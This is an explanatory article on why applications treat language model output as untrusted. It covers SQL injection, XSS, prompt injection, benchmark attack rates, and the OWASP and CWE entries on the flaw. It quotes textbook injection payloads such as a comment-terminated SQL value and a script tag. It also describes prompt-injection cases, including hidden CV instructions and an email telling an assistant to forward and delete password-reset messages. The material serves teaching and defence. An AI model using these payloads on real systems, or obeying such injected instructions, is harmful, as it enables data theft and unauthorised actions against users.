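# Treating language model output as untrusted input to downstream systems

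## How model output reaches other software, and how injection flaws work

Treating language model output as untrusted input is a software security practice in which an application checks or rewrites the model's output before other software acts on it, or restricts what that software can do. Text is untrusted if someone with no authority over the system may have influenced it, even if the text is true and well meant. Well-built websites, for example, check what strangers type into web forms even though most of it is harmless.

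Treating model output as untrusted matters because many applications now pass it to a browser or a database, which may run code or commands it contains, rather than only showing it to a person. Security engineers call a component that receives data and acts on it a sink. The term appears in *CWE-74*, the general entry on injection in a public catalogue of software flaws that the American non-profit MITRE maintains. Flaws at sinks are decades older than language models, and the old cases are the easiest to understand.

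### One answer and where it goes

Office assistants that run on language models are a common kind of product. An imaginary one reads an employee's email and the company's shared files, answers in formatted text, queries the company database and runs short programs that the model writes. An employee in accounts asks it how much the company still owes a paper supplier.

The model replies with a series of tokens, numbers that each stand for a word or a piece of a word. It generates them one at a time, each based on everything before it, and ordinary code converts them into a string, the same type of object as a string from a web form. Nothing in the string marks which words come from the employee's question and which from the supplier's email. At this point, nothing has happened yet in the outside world. When an assistant "runs a query", the model writes a request in an agreed format, and the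 application around it reads the request and sends the query.

To look up the amount, the assistant first sends the database a query in SQL, the language programs use to communicate with most databases. The model receives the result and writes a few lines of Python to add up the invoices, and a Python interpreter runs them. The employee also wants a copy on the shared drive, so the model supplies a file name, and the file system writes to whatever location that name specifies.

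The answer comes in Markdown, a notation that marks headings, links and images with punctuation. The application converts it to HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser displays the page. If the answer includes an image, the browser sends a network request to the image's address without the user clicking anything. A colleague who uses the same assistant from the command line gets the answer in a terminal, where certain invisible characters move the cursor or change the display. The assistant may also pass its summary to another agent, a second model with its own tools, which schedules payments and takes the summary as part of its instructions.

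Most of these routes are common enough to appear in *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in a list of the ten main risks of language model applications from OWASP, a non-profit foundation for software security. The entry covers shells, browsers, SQL queries, file paths and email templates. In one of its scenarios, a chatbot passes an unchecked reply to an extension that also has administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance.

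### Data and commands

All these sinks read text in some formal language and do what the text specifies. A database, for example, first parses a query by splitting it into units and using the grammar of SQL to determine each unit's role. A few characters determine the structure. A single quotation mark opens a piece of text and the next one closes it, so anything between them is data and anything outside them can be a command. The database receives only the query's characters, with no record of who wrote which ones.

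Su and Wassermann (2006) point out in *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications* that databases interpret queries as structured commands, while the web applications that build them often treat them as plain sequences of characters. Injection flaws arise from this difference in how the two handle a query.

A textbook case comes from PortSwigger's *SQL injection*, a tutorial by a maker of security testing tools. A shop's website lists products by category. When a visitor clicks on "Gifts", the site takes the category from the web address, glues it between two fixed pieces of text and sends the database this query:

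```
SELECT * FROM products WHERE category = 'Gifts' AND released = 1
```

The last condition hides products that the shop has not yet released. Now a visitor edits the address so that the category reads `Gifts'--`. The query becomes:

```
SELECT * FROM products WHERE category = 'Gifts'--' AND released = 1
```

The visitor's quotation mark closes the text early. Two hyphens begin a comment in SQL, so the database ignores the rest of the line, including the condition about release, and the page shows the hidden products. The database works correctly throughout. According to MITRE, an injection requires only that the data be parsed, whereas an attacker exploiting a flaw such as a buffer overflow needs some further fault to gain control.

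Banning the quotation mark is a poor fix because legitimate input can contain it. MITRE's *CWE-89*, the catalogue's entry on SQL injection, gives the surname O'Reilly as an example. A site that refuses apostrophes can't accept the name, and a site that strips them records it incorrectly. The sounder repair is the parameterised query. The application sends the query with a placeholder for the category and supplies the category separately. The structure of the query is already fixed by then, so the database can use the visitor's text only as a value.

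Su and Wassermann offered the first formal definition of where data ends and command begins in web applications. A parser turns a query into a tree, with the whole query at the root and single words and values at the tips. Legitimate input fills one complete node of that tree, as the name John fills a single piece of quoted text. In an attack, the input extends beyond a single node into the surrounding structure. In one of their examples, an online shop neutralises every quotation mark but also accepts a number for the credit card type. Numbers need no quotation marks in SQL, so a visitor can add an always-true condition after the number and receive every card number in the table without typing a quotation mark.

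Ray and Ligatti (2012), in *Defining Code-injection Attacks*, showed that the tree test misses some attacks and flags some harmless input. If a visitor enters the function call `exit()` in place of a PIN, the input fills exactly one node. Unless someone has forbidden function calls there, the input passes and the database executes the function. If a visitor types a file name and its extension into two boxes, and the program joins them with a dot inside one piece of quoted text, neither input fills a node, so the test wrongly reports an attack.

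Their own definition depends on whether the input still has to be evaluated. Input counts as data if it ends up inside a finished value, such as a number or a quoted string, and any injected symbol outside such a value is code. They also proved, for a simplified version of SQL, that every application that always copies some untrusted input verbatim into its query is open to attack. The flaw is therefore the copying itself, regardless of which characters an attacker uses.

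Cross-site scripting (XSS) is the same flaw with a browser as the sink. HTML uses angle brackets to separate a page's structure from its text, and the `<SCRIPT>` tag marks what follows as a program. The standard example is in *CERT Advisory CA-2000-02 Malicious HTML Tags Embedded in Client Web Requests* (2000), from the CERT Coordination Center, a security response team at Carnegie Mellon University. Someone posts a greeting on a message board that includes `<SCRIPT>malicious code</SCRIPT>`. If the site copies the message into its page unchanged, the browser of everyone who opens the page runs the script. The script runs with the site's privileges, so it can read the page's contents, including what the reader has typed into a form, and send them elsewhere. The name "cross-site" refers to one source injecting code into pages that another source sends. The usual repair is encoding, which replaces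 special characters with forms that a browser displays but does not execute.

According to the CERT Coordination Center, message boards had long guarded against this. Many sites overlooked text that is shown only to the visitor who submits it. Such text can still be hostile, because the visitor may have followed a link that somebody else wrote with the hostile text inside it. A chatbot's answer is easy to misjudge in the same way. It appears only on the screen of the employee who asked, so it looks like a private exchange with the assistant, though some of its wording may come from the supplier.

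### Text that waits in storage

In the shop example, the hostile text took effect as soon as it arrived. In second-order injection, also called stored injection, an application first saves the text safely, but the text causes damage later, when another part of the system reads it back and puts it into a command.

PortSwigger explains why careful developers miss this flaw. Knowing about SQL injection, they use a safe method to put a customer's name into the database. Later, the author of a different piece of code assumes the name is safe because it comes from the company's own database, and inserts it directly into a new query. But the safe method was designed to store the name exactly as typed, including any hostile characters. Su and Wassermann describe a variant in which users can save search conditions under a label of their choice. A malicious user saves a condition that also deletes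 a table, gives it a dull label and leaves it for a colleague to run.

The office assistant creates many such delays. Suppose it summarises a supplier's email and saves the summary in the supplier's record. A month later a manager opens a dashboard that displays the record. The supplier's wording can reach that dashboard without the supplier having an account on either system. The programmer who built the dashboard may never have heard of the assistant, and had no reason to think that an outsider's wording could reach the summary field.

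### Prompt injection

A language model also acts on the text it receives, so it can be a sink as well as a source of text for other sinks. In an example from MITRE, an application asks a visitor for the catalogue numbers of two software flaws, inserts them into a sentence that asks a chatbot to explain the difference, and prints the reply. The programmer has encoded the reply, so no script can reach the browser. But a visitor who types a request for a pirate poem after the second number gets some pirate verse along with the explanation. This is direct prompt injection, in which an attacker types text that makes the model follow the attacker's instructions. The application can prevent it here by refusing anything that doesn't have the fixed form of a catalogue number, but nobody can write a comparable rule for the body of an email.

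In indirect prompt injection, the attacker puts instructions in a page, email or file that the model will read, without interacting with the application directly. Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, demonstrated such attacks on Bing's chat service and on code-completion tools. They noted that, until then, the usual assumption was that the user prompts the model. David C (2025), a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter's system that scores CVs, one of which contains hidden text telling the model to approve the candidate, in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. *Generative AI Models* (2024), a report on risks for industry and public authorities, mentions that instructions can also be hidden using special Unicode characters that a model processes but a reader doesn't see.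 If an assistant has access to email, the attacker only needs to send it a message. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, imagines a message that asks the assistant to forward its owner's password reset emails and then delete them.

Simon Willison, a software developer, coined the term "prompt injection" in 2022 and modelled it on SQL injection. Both happen because a program joins trusted and untrusted text into one string, but the remedy for SQL injection does not work for prompt injection. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) points out that parameterised queries work because SQL has a grammar. A parser can use it to fix the structure of a query before any outside value arrives. According to David C, SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010 and are now rare in websites. English has no comparable grammar for a parser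 to use. Ray and Ligatti's definition also fails here because it assumes a language with finished values, which leave nothing to act on, and no wording in an email is guaranteed to have that effect on a model.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) formally describes how this difficulty extends to the model's design. Let *s* be the developer's trusted instructions and *u* the untrusted text. The prompt is *s* followed by *u*, a single sequence of tokens *x*₁, …, *x*ₙ. One function *E* turns every token into a vector, a list of numbers, and the model works on *E*(*x*₁), …, *E*(*x*ₙ). Each token has a trusted or untrusted origin, but *E* does not record it, so the word "delete" yields the same vector whether it appears in *s* or *u*. The paper counts tool calls and memory writes, as well as text, among a model's actions. An assistant that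 keeps notes can therefore save a hostile sentence and later read it back as part of its own prompt, which is second-order injection with the model as the sink.

Chat systems label each part of a conversation as coming from the developer, the user or the model, but those labels are tokens in the same sequence as the text they mark. *LLMON* (2026), a proposal for a markup language for prompts, notes that they do not reliably enforce a separation of instructions from data. *Structural Role Injection in Handlebars-Templated LLM Prompts* (2026) describes the result as one flat stream in which the model must infer which passages carry authority. Labelling a passage as data only makes a model less likely to follow instructions in it, whereas a database cannot execute a value supplied through a placeholder, whatever the value contains.

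*A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists ideas for separating instructions from data in the prompt, such as typed regions and training that teaches models to respect labels. David C doubts that any of these will stop prompt injection completely, because they impose the distinction on a technology that has none and only predicts the next token. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* concludes that the separation has to come from outside the model. There is a basis for this on the output side, because the SQL queries and web pages that the model helps to produce have a grammar that keeps commands apart from data, which the prompt lacks.

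## Why model output counts as untrusted, and what that does not mean

The argument for checking model output before a sink acts on it consists of three claims about an application:

1. What the model reads influences what it writes.
2. Some of what the model reads comes from people with no authority over the system.
3. Some sinks act on the output they receive.

If all three are true, a person with no authority can influence what a sink does, unless something between the model and the sink prevents it. This argument doesn't depend on the model's intentions. OWASP reasons that because prompts can control the output, an application that passes it on unchecked in effect gives users indirect access to functions they were never offered. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre gives the same reasoning in its guidance.

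The argument applies only when its claims all hold for the same piece of output. If an application shows replies as plain text in a window that interprets no markup, no sink acts on them. If a model only sorts product codes that the company itself assigns, no outsider has influenced its output. In either case, the argument is no reason to check the output. Most objections are that some real application fits one of these safe cases.

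### Users who attack their own session

A user who types a hostile prompt and gets a hostile answer back in their own browser gains nothing if they wrote everything the model read, are the only person who sees the answer, and can reach no other sink. They could already run whatever they like in that browser.

Few applications are that simple. In one of OWASP's scenarios, a web application generates content from a user's prompt, and a script in that content runs in another person's browser. The office assistant would have this flaw if it drafted notices for the company's intranet, because content generated from one employee's prompt would reach everyone's screen. The assistant's other sinks don't belong to the user either. The Python interpreter runs on the company's server, so an employee who gets the model to write a particular program may be able to do things there that their own login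 doesn't permit.

With indirect injection the objection fails altogether, because the hostile wording comes from the supplier and not from the employee.

### Internal documents and filtered inputs

Limiting an assistant to internal documents, which developers sometimes cite as a safeguard, does not keep out text written by outsiders. The argument depends on who wrote a file, and "internal" usually describes only where it is stored. Suppliers' emails, job applications and scanned invoices are all stored in internal folders. According to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, code repositories and tool responses can also carry injected instructions, and both are often internal too. Authority also varies among staff. An intern who can save a file to the shared drive may have no say over payments, but the assistant may read that file when the finance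 director asks it a question.

The objection succeeds if the company can name everyone who can write to a source and would let any of them command the sink directly. A price list that only the database administrators can edit might pass this test, but a shared drive won't.

Screening the input for hostile instructions does not make a model's output trustworthy. Willison is suspicious of products that advertise catching 95% of attacks, a rate he calls "very much a failing grade" in web security. An attacker can keep rewording a message to look for a version the filter misses. Filters also check whether text reads like an instruction to a model, which doesn't show whether its characters are safe to put in a database query. The surname O'Reilly would pass any sensible filter, but its apostrophe can break a carelessly built query. An input filter can still be worth having because it reduces the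 number of attacks that reach the model.

### How often current models follow injected instructions

Evidence supports the objection that newer models resist injection much better than older ones. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Anthropic's Claude Opus 5, working as a browser agent, failed in all 129 test scenarios. Developers publish their tests of a new model in a system card. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for the later Claude Opus 5.5 gives similar or better results on every injection test it reports. According to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), the share of indirect attacks that failed in the company's own tests rose from 96.23% with GPT-5.6 Sol to 99.79% with GPT-6 Astra.

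Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, analysed a public competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attack attempts against 13 models from 2025. Each of the 41 scenarios gave the attacker control of one piece of outside text, such as an email or a code comment. In most scenarios, the attacker had to make the model both perform a harmful action and hide it from the user in its final answer. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The attackers could see the conversation and knew which action they had to trigger, so Dziemian and colleagues treat these rates as an upper bound on vulnerability to a single-turn attack, not as an estimate of how often attacks happen in practice.

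Gray Swan, the security company that ran the competition, turns successful attacks into a benchmark for newer models. The security vendor PromptArmor has a separate benchmark, *FrontierBreach*. It uses long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio, and plants attacks modelled on ones its researchers have found in real products. The table gives attack success rates from both benchmarks. The Gray Swan figures come from OpenAI for its own models and from The Decoder for Claude Opus 5, and the two sources' figures may not be based on the same set of attacks.

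| Model | Gray Swan, within 15 attempts | FrontierBreach |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | – | 2.4% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 8.5% | 7.6% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | 10.0% |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | – | 10.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 27.0% | 33.3% |
| Kimi K3.1 Pro | – | 50.0% |
| Grok 4.5 | – | 91.4% |

PromptArmor sells protection against these attacks, so it has an interest in finding high rates, and its margins of error are around four percentage points for GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5. Even so, the model that failed 2.0% of the time on one benchmark and never in a browser test failed 10.0% of the time on office tasks. A success rate therefore applies to a particular combination of model, attacks and setting. The setting alone can make a large difference. VentureBeat reports that none of 200 attempts succeeded against Claude Opus 4.6, from February 2026, in a constrained coding environment. When the same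 model operated a graphical interface, 17.8% of single attempts succeeded, and by the 200th attempt the attacker had succeeded in 78.6% of cases. Additional safeguards only reduced that to 57.1%.

Repetition matters because an outsider who can send one email can usually send many. If each attempt succeeded independently with probability *p*, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts would be 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ. At 17.8% per attempt, this gives 79% after eight attempts. Claude Opus 4.6 took 200 to reach about that level, so the attempts were clearly not independent. Attacks succeeded quickly in some situations and almost never in others. By the same formula, GPT-6 Astra's failure rate of 0.21% would give an attacker a 50% chance of at least one success after about 330 attempts. The true number is probably higher in most situations and lower in a few weak ones, and a developer doesn't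 know in advance which are weak.

Zero successful attacks in 129 scenarios is also weaker evidence than it looks. Even if the scenarios were a random sample of everything a browser agent encounters, the result would be compatible, at the 95% confidence level, with attacks succeeding in up to about 2.3% of situations. Attackers also adapt, and Dziemian and colleagues note that newer attacks have easily bypassed defences whose makers had reported a 0% attack success rate. According to The Decoder, OpenAI itself said in December 2025 that prompt injection may never be fully solved.

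Incident counts offer some evidence on the other side. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* covers the August 2026 edition of OWASP's list, in which practitioners ranked prompt injection first for the third year running. It would not have made the top ten based on recorded incidents alone. OWASP says this is because security teams fight injection hard, so fewer successful attacks reach public databases. That may be right, but the count would also be low if the threat were small.

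A model with a perfect score on prompt injection tests can still produce unsafe output, because text can influence a model's output without the model obeying it. Suppose an employee asks for the exact wording of a supplier's delivery note, and the note contains a script tag. The model will copy the tag because the employee asked for the exact wording. If the application puts the reply into a page unchanged, the browser runs the script. Lower injection rates make it harder for an attacker to choose the output freely, but they don't stop the model from copying text, which summarising and quoting tools are meant to do.

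### Dangerous output without an attacker

A string can also do damage when nobody meant any harm. If the office assistant tidies a shared drive and writes a command to delete a folder called "Old invoices" without quotation marks, the shell reads two names and may delete a different folder called "invoices". If it names a file "Payments 03/2026", many file systems will treat the slash as a boundary between folders. A developer who looks only for attackers may miss both mistakes.

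In one OWASP scenario, a user asks a chat feature for a query that deletes every table in a database, and the application runs the query without checking it. In another, a coding model suggests a software package that does not exist. The model makes this error first, and an attacker may later exploit it by publishing something under the invented name.

OpenAI tested GPT-6 Astra in simulated workplaces with messaging, email and sales software. The tasks were designed to provoke mistakes through ambiguous instructions, similar-looking resources and complex permissions, but each could be completed safely. Under the default policy, which tells the model when to ask the user for approval, it still carried out unauthorised transactions in 4.3% of the relevant tests and moved private data where it shouldn't in 4.5%. The overall rate of bad outcomes was 3.0%, compared with 8.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol. These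 rates should be lower in ordinary office work. But a payment system receives the same request whether the model is confused or an attacker has manipulated it, and a check there can stop the request in either case.

### False answers, excessive powers and injection itself

Misinformation is a separate problem, because untrusted text can be true. OWASP defines misinformation as incorrect, incomplete, unsupported or misleading output that seems credible enough to influence a person, an automated workflow or an agent. If the assistant tells the employee that the company owes €4,000 when it owes €40,000, the application can encode the answer correctly and the browser will safely display the wrong amount. The delivery note with a script in it is dangerous to display even when the assistant quotes it accurately. To prevent misinformation, OWASP advises basing answers on authoritative, current sources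 and verifying claims before acting on them, which would not have stopped the script. Invented package names involve both problems, because the model falsely states that a package exists and the installer acts on that statement.

OWASP uses the term "excessive agency" for a model that can do too much damage when its output is unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated. The causes are excessive functionality, permissions and autonomy. Suppose an office assistant only needs to read invoices, but its developers also gave it a tool for making payments. A request to pay the wrong supplier can have a valid account number, a plausible amount and perfect formatting, so checking its form won't catch the error. The fix is to remove the payment tool or require a person's approval. Excessive agency overlaps with unsafe output handling when an application has to restrict what generated code can reach, because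 this also limits what the model can do.

Prompt injection happens earlier, when the model reads hostile text and changes its behaviour. Checking the output limits what the attacker can achieve afterwards but doesn't prevent the injection, and some attacks need no dangerous string at all. In one of Dziemian and colleagues' scenarios, a hidden instruction tells an email assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. The user misses the deadline even if the developer has secured every sink against injected code, because the summary is harmless to every parser.

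Output checks have a good record against data theft. Willison lists more than a dozen products, including ChatGPT, Slack and GitHub Copilot Chat, in which researchers showed that injected instructions could carry data out. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the route through which the data left, though the models could presumably still be fooled. According to Infosecurity Magazine, the 2026 edition of OWASP's list generalizes this approach. It recommends assuming that an attacker will eventually get past the model's instructions, and restricting what the model may do and what its output may reach.

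### The model as a user

OWASP summarizes the principle as treating the model like any other user. This works well for the form of the output, because web applications already check what users type, and many of the same checks apply.

Authority is harder to check. When an employee presses a delete button, the application checks whether that employee may delete the record. An assistant often has a single service account with enough rights to serve everybody in the company. If the application checks only that account's permissions, the deletion is nearly always allowed, and a supplier whose email has shaped the request in effect uses the account's rights. Security engineers call such a program a confused deputy because it uses its legitimate authority on behalf of someone who has none. OWASP lists privileges beyond those of the end user among the conditions that make the flaw worse. The advice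 is too weak if it is read as trusting the model's own service account.

A better reading is that the system should check each request against the rights of the person using the assistant. In an accounts clerk's session, the assistant could then do only what the clerk could do by hand. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, likewise recommends applying the same guardrails to output that triggers actions as to any external request, with protection against attempts to bypass authorisation.

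This still lets the supplier use the clerk's rights, which may include reading every other supplier's invoices. A stricter rule would allow an action only if everyone whose text the model has read may take it. Since the supplier may take no actions, the assistant would have to stop work as soon as it opened its first email. Willison quotes a paper on design patterns that takes a middle course, requiring the system to make it impossible for untrusted input to trigger consequential actions once an agent has taken it in. Under this rule the assistant could go on summarising emails, but a payment would have to wait for the clerk.

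The advice is too strong for some sinks. A sensible shop doesn't let visitors submit Python programs to its server or write their own database queries. An application that treated the model exactly like a visitor would refuse both, but writing such programs and queries is a large part of the office assistant's purpose.

### Output that is meant to act

Treating model output as untrusted is hard when the output is meant to run as code, because encoding it to make it safe also stops it from working. Suppose the model writes a short program to flag large invoices, with the line `if total > limit:`. Encoding for HTML changes the line to `if total &gt; limit:`, which a browser displays correctly and Python rejects as an error. Encoding for Python would turn the whole program into a quoted string, which the interpreter would store without running. By Ray and Ligatti's definition, all of a generated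 program is injected code. Placeholders don't solve the problem for databases either if the model writes the structure of the query as well as the values.

The objection succeeds if "untrusted" means that the application must neutralise every command. The three claims support a weaker requirement, that a component other than the model must decide what the output may do at each sink. How that component can do this depends on what the sink is meant to do with the text, which gives six kinds of measure.

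If the sink should only display the text, the application can encode it without affecting any legitimate use. If the display needs some markup, such as headings and bold type, sanitising removes all other markup.

Other output has a fixed form, such as a date, an expense category or a payment request with four named fields, so the application can validate it and reject anything else. Validation is stricter than encoding because it also rejects harmless but unexpected values.

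Valid syntax doesn't make a model-generated program safe to run. Two programs can both be valid Python and differ only in which files they delete, and no general procedure can determine from a program's text everything it will do when it runs. The application therefore has to run the program in a sandbox, where it can't reach the files and networks it could damage.

Some short strings are valid but still dangerous because of what they refer to. A valid package name may point to code that an attacker published yesterday, and an image address may point to an attacker's server. The application has to check such names against a list or registry because the string doesn't show who controls what it names.

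A password in a model's answer is dangerous because of who or what receives it, not because a browser or database will misinterpret it. Scanning the answer before it is sent can catch secrets with a recognisable format, but a model can also disclose a secret in words that match no pattern.

None of these checks can show whether the account number in a payment request came from the company's records or from the supplier's latest email, because the number has the right form in both cases. To distinguish the two, the application has to track where the data came from and pass that information to the payment system. Models make this harder because they combine everything in the prompt. Unless the design keeps sources separate, a cautious system has to mark the whole output as untrusted if the prompt contains even one untrusted document.

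## How OWASP and the CWE define the flaw

Two public references name and number the flaw of acting on unchecked model output. OWASP's list ranks the risks of language model applications. MITRE's Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) sorts software flaws by the underlying mistake, so CWE-89 means SQL injection in any product. A separate system, CVE, numbers individual flaws, such as one in a particular version of a chat program. Whoever files a CVE record normally adds the CWE number of the mistake behind the flaw, and counts of how often each type of flaw occurs rely on those numbers.

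Neither the OWASP list nor the CWE has legal force. According to Respan's *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026), a guide from a company that sells tests for language model applications, OWASP is a foundation, not a regulator or standards body. It offers its documents as guidance, but auditors and corporate buyers treat them as a baseline. MITRE can mark a CWE number as discouraged, but companies can still put it on their records.

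### Three editions of OWASP's entry

OWASP first listed the flaw in 2023 as LLM02, Insecure Output Handling. It defined the flaw as insufficient "validation, sanitization, and handling" of a model's output before it passes to other components. The 2025 edition, dated 18 November 2024, renamed it Improper Output Handling and renumbered it LLM05 but kept the definition. The definition places the flaw between the model and the next component, so if a model writes a script tag and an application sends it to a browser unchanged, the flaw is in the application, not the model.

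OWASP says the flaw can lead to XSS and cross-site request forgery in browsers. In cross-site request forgery, a hostile page makes a visitor's browser send a request to another site where the visitor is logged in. On servers, the flaw can let an attacker gain extra privileges, run code, or make the server contact addresses the attacker can't reach directly.

The 2023 entry gave two examples. In one, an application passes model output straight into a shell or a function such as `eval`, which runs text as code. In the other, a browser interprets JavaScript or Markdown from the model. OWASP added three more in the 2025 edition: SQL queries that run without proper parameters, file paths that can lead outside the intended folder, and email templates that an attacker can use for phishing.

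The 2023 entry made three recommendations, which come first in the 2025 list of seven:

1. Treat the model like any other user, and validate its responses before they reach backend functions.
2. Follow the Application Security Verification Standard (ASVS), another OWASP document, when validating and sanitising.
3. Encode output that goes back to users, so that JavaScript or Markdown in it doesn't run.
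4. Choose the encoding to suit the sink, such as HTML encoding for web pages and SQL escaping for databases.
5. Use parameterised queries for every database operation that involves model output.
6. Set a strict Content Security Policy (CSP), a web page's instruction to the browser about which scripts may run and which addresses it may contact.
7. Log and monitor output for unusual patterns that might indicate an attack.

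OWASP's seven recommendations don't cover all of its own examples. In one, a chat feature writes a query that deletes every table. A parameterised query doesn't help there, because the deletion is part of the query's structure, not a value. The recommendations don't include a sandbox or narrower permissions.

One OWASP scenario is also misleading about the cause. It describes a model's unsanitised script running in a victim's browser, which OWASP attributes to "insufficient validation of prompts". A developer who took this literally would screen the prompts but leave the model's output unencoded on the page. According to Respan, the 2026 edition separates the two problems more carefully and covers checks on model input under the entry on prompt injection.

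OWASP (2026) released the 2026 edition of its LLM Top 10 on 3 August 2026, and Improper Output Handling became LLM10. In its announcement, OWASP promised expanded threat coverage but did not list the changes, so the details come from security vendors. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) reports two additions to the entry: terminals and code editors that interpret ANSI escape sequences, the invisible codes that control a text display, and programs that automatically fetch resources named in the output, which can send private data to an attacker. Advait Patel, a security engineer who leads another OWASP project, described the same two additions to ReversingLabs, a software security company. Only Respan mentions a third addition, insecure code that assistants write at scale.

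Terminals are new to the entry, while auto-fetching adds detail to an existing scenario. Since 2023, the entry has described a website summariser that sends a user's private data to an attacker's server, without explaining how the data leaves. Naming the program that fetches the resource lets developers identify which component to change.

Insecure generated code fits the entry less well, although Respan calls it the same failure at a different point in the pipeline, and a scenario in the 2025 edition already had a coding model introducing SQL injection flaws. If a coding assistant writes a login page with such a flaw, no encoding step between the assistant and the code repository could remove it, because the program is legitimate but badly written. Someone has to review the code. The damage comes later, when an attacker finds what is by then an ordinary case of CWE-89. Respan reports that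 OWASP assigns the unsafe use of output to this entry and incorrect output to Misinformation, and insecure code could reasonably go under either.

The renumbering also affects companies that cite the list in contracts or test reports, because "LLM05" without a year could mean Improper Output Handling or, since August 2026, Data and Model Poisoning.

### From fifth place to tenth

The entry has fallen from second place in 2023 to fifth in 2025 and tenth in 2026. The 2023 and 2025 rankings came from a vote among practitioners. For 2026, the project also used data on 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases and a database of harms caused by AI. Steve Wilson, the project's founder, told ReversingLabs that the project built classifiers to read the records, and that 6,639 had enough detail to sort. The other 14% did not contribute to the ranking.

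An entry's combined score is 0.75*V* + 0.25*I*, where *V* is its score in the vote and *I* is its score in the incident data. The project leaders gave the vote more weight so that one noisy year of data couldn't override it. They say the data's one-quarter weight is enough to move an entry by a tier when the vote and the data differ widely.

The project must have scored entries on something finer than their positions in the two rankings, such as the size of each entry's vote, or made an adjustment by hand. Prompt injection came first in the vote but would have fallen out of the top ten on incidents alone, so its weighted average position would be at least 0.75 × 1 + 0.25 × 11 = 3.5. Invicti reports that the vote and the data fully agreed on sensitive information disclosure, which came second overall. If it was second in both, its average would be 2, and ranking by position would have put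 it first. Neither Invicti nor ReversingLabs gives the scoring scale, or output handling's separate results in the vote and the data, so their accounts don't show which of the two pushed that entry down.

Patel and Invicti both say that output handling fell because the risks above it became more urgent, not because it became safer. That accounts for part of the fall. All five entries that ranked below it in 2025 overtook it, but only three of them moved up the list: excessive agency, misinformation and unbounded consumption (uncontrolled use of a model that can run up huge bills). The other two, hidden context exposure and weaknesses in vector databases, each dropped one place. The change of method may also have contributed, because a ranking based on votes and one that includes incidents measure different things, so an entry can fall without any change in the risk.

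A vulnerability database mostly records flaws that someone has found in a product, whether or not anyone has exploited them. The incident data is therefore not a measure of harm, although Patel told ReversingLabs that it shows what has caused damage in the real world. Such a database also tends to miss software that a company builds for itself. If the company quietly fixed a serious flaw in the office assistant, no public record would exist.

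It is also unclear whether the data includes output handling flaws filed under another name. Suppose a commercial chatbot displays a model's reply without encoding it, and a researcher reports the flaw as XSS. If the researcher doesn't mention the model, a search for incidents involving language models will probably miss the report. Otherwise, a classifier could put the case under output handling or prompt injection, depending on which part of the attack the researcher emphasises. Invicti, Respan and ReversingLabs don't explain in their accounts how the project treated such cases.

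Many incidents fit several entries. If a supplier's email makes the office assistant send invoices to an outside server, the cause is prompt injection, the missing check is output handling, and the result is disclosure of sensitive information. If the model also had more access than it needed, that is excessive agency. A single label records the incident under only one of these entries. *Thoughts on the 2025 OWASP Top 10 for LLMs release* similarly criticizes the entry on vector databases, arguing that OWASP could distribute its contents among prompt injection, excessive agency and supply chain risks. OWASP has also had a separate list for agents since December 2025, and Respan notes that many real incidents lie on the boundary between the two lists.

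OWASP attributes the low count of prompt injection to defenders working hard to prevent it. The same could be true of output handling, since developers have been encoding output for web pages for decades. A low count could mean that the flaw is rare, that defences work, or that people file it under another category, and the rank doesn't show which. The rank is still a useful summary of what several hundred practitioners think the industry should address first. But a developer whose application passes model output to a shell should worry about the flaw wherever it ranks.

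### CWE-1426 and why MITRE discourages its use

The closest equivalent in MITRE's CWE is CWE-1426, Improper Validation of Generative AI Output. It applies when a product uses a generative AI component whose output it can't directly control and doesn't check that output well enough against the "intended security, content, or privacy policy".

The CWE's definition is broader than OWASP's in that it includes output that breaks a content policy. A children's homework app that displays a violent story has this weakness, even though the browser displays the text safely. The definition is also narrower because it covers only validation, so an application that fails to encode output when it should has a different weakness.

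In the catalogue's hierarchy, CWE-1426 comes under CWE-707, Improper Neutralization, one of the most abstract entries. MITRE also includes it in a category for injection. It suggests four mitigations:

- Run the AI component in an untrusted or non-privileged space, because its output can't be trusted.
- Use "semantic comparators", which look for things that appear different but have similar meanings.
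- Monitor the output with external components, often called supervisors or guardrails.
- Use good and bad examples in training to guide the model's output.

A working group on AI wrote the entry in June and July 2024. MITRE published it in version 4.15 of the catalogue on 16 July, deciding that it was more useful to release the entry quickly and add to it later. In version 4.17, from April 2025, MITRE still advised against using the number for real vulnerabilities, because the entry might change and people often misinterpret it. It advises analysts to look for the root cause and suggests more specific numbers:

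- CWE-77, command injection, for most prompt injection attacks, or CWE-78 if the attack injects an operating system command.
- CWE-94, code injection, if the product feeds output directly into a component that parses and executes code.
- CWE-116, improper encoding or escaping of output, if the product should have encoded the output.

For the office assistant, running the model's Python without restrictions would be CWE-94, while displaying the script tag from the delivery note would be CWE-116. The advice makes sense for repairs because a programmer who sees "CWE-116" knows to fix the encoding, whereas "improper validation of AI output" doesn't identify a particular repair. MITRE observes that many flaws reported as prompt injection look like ordinary injection, except that the input comes from a model's output rather than directly from an attacker. It compares them to second-order SQL injection.

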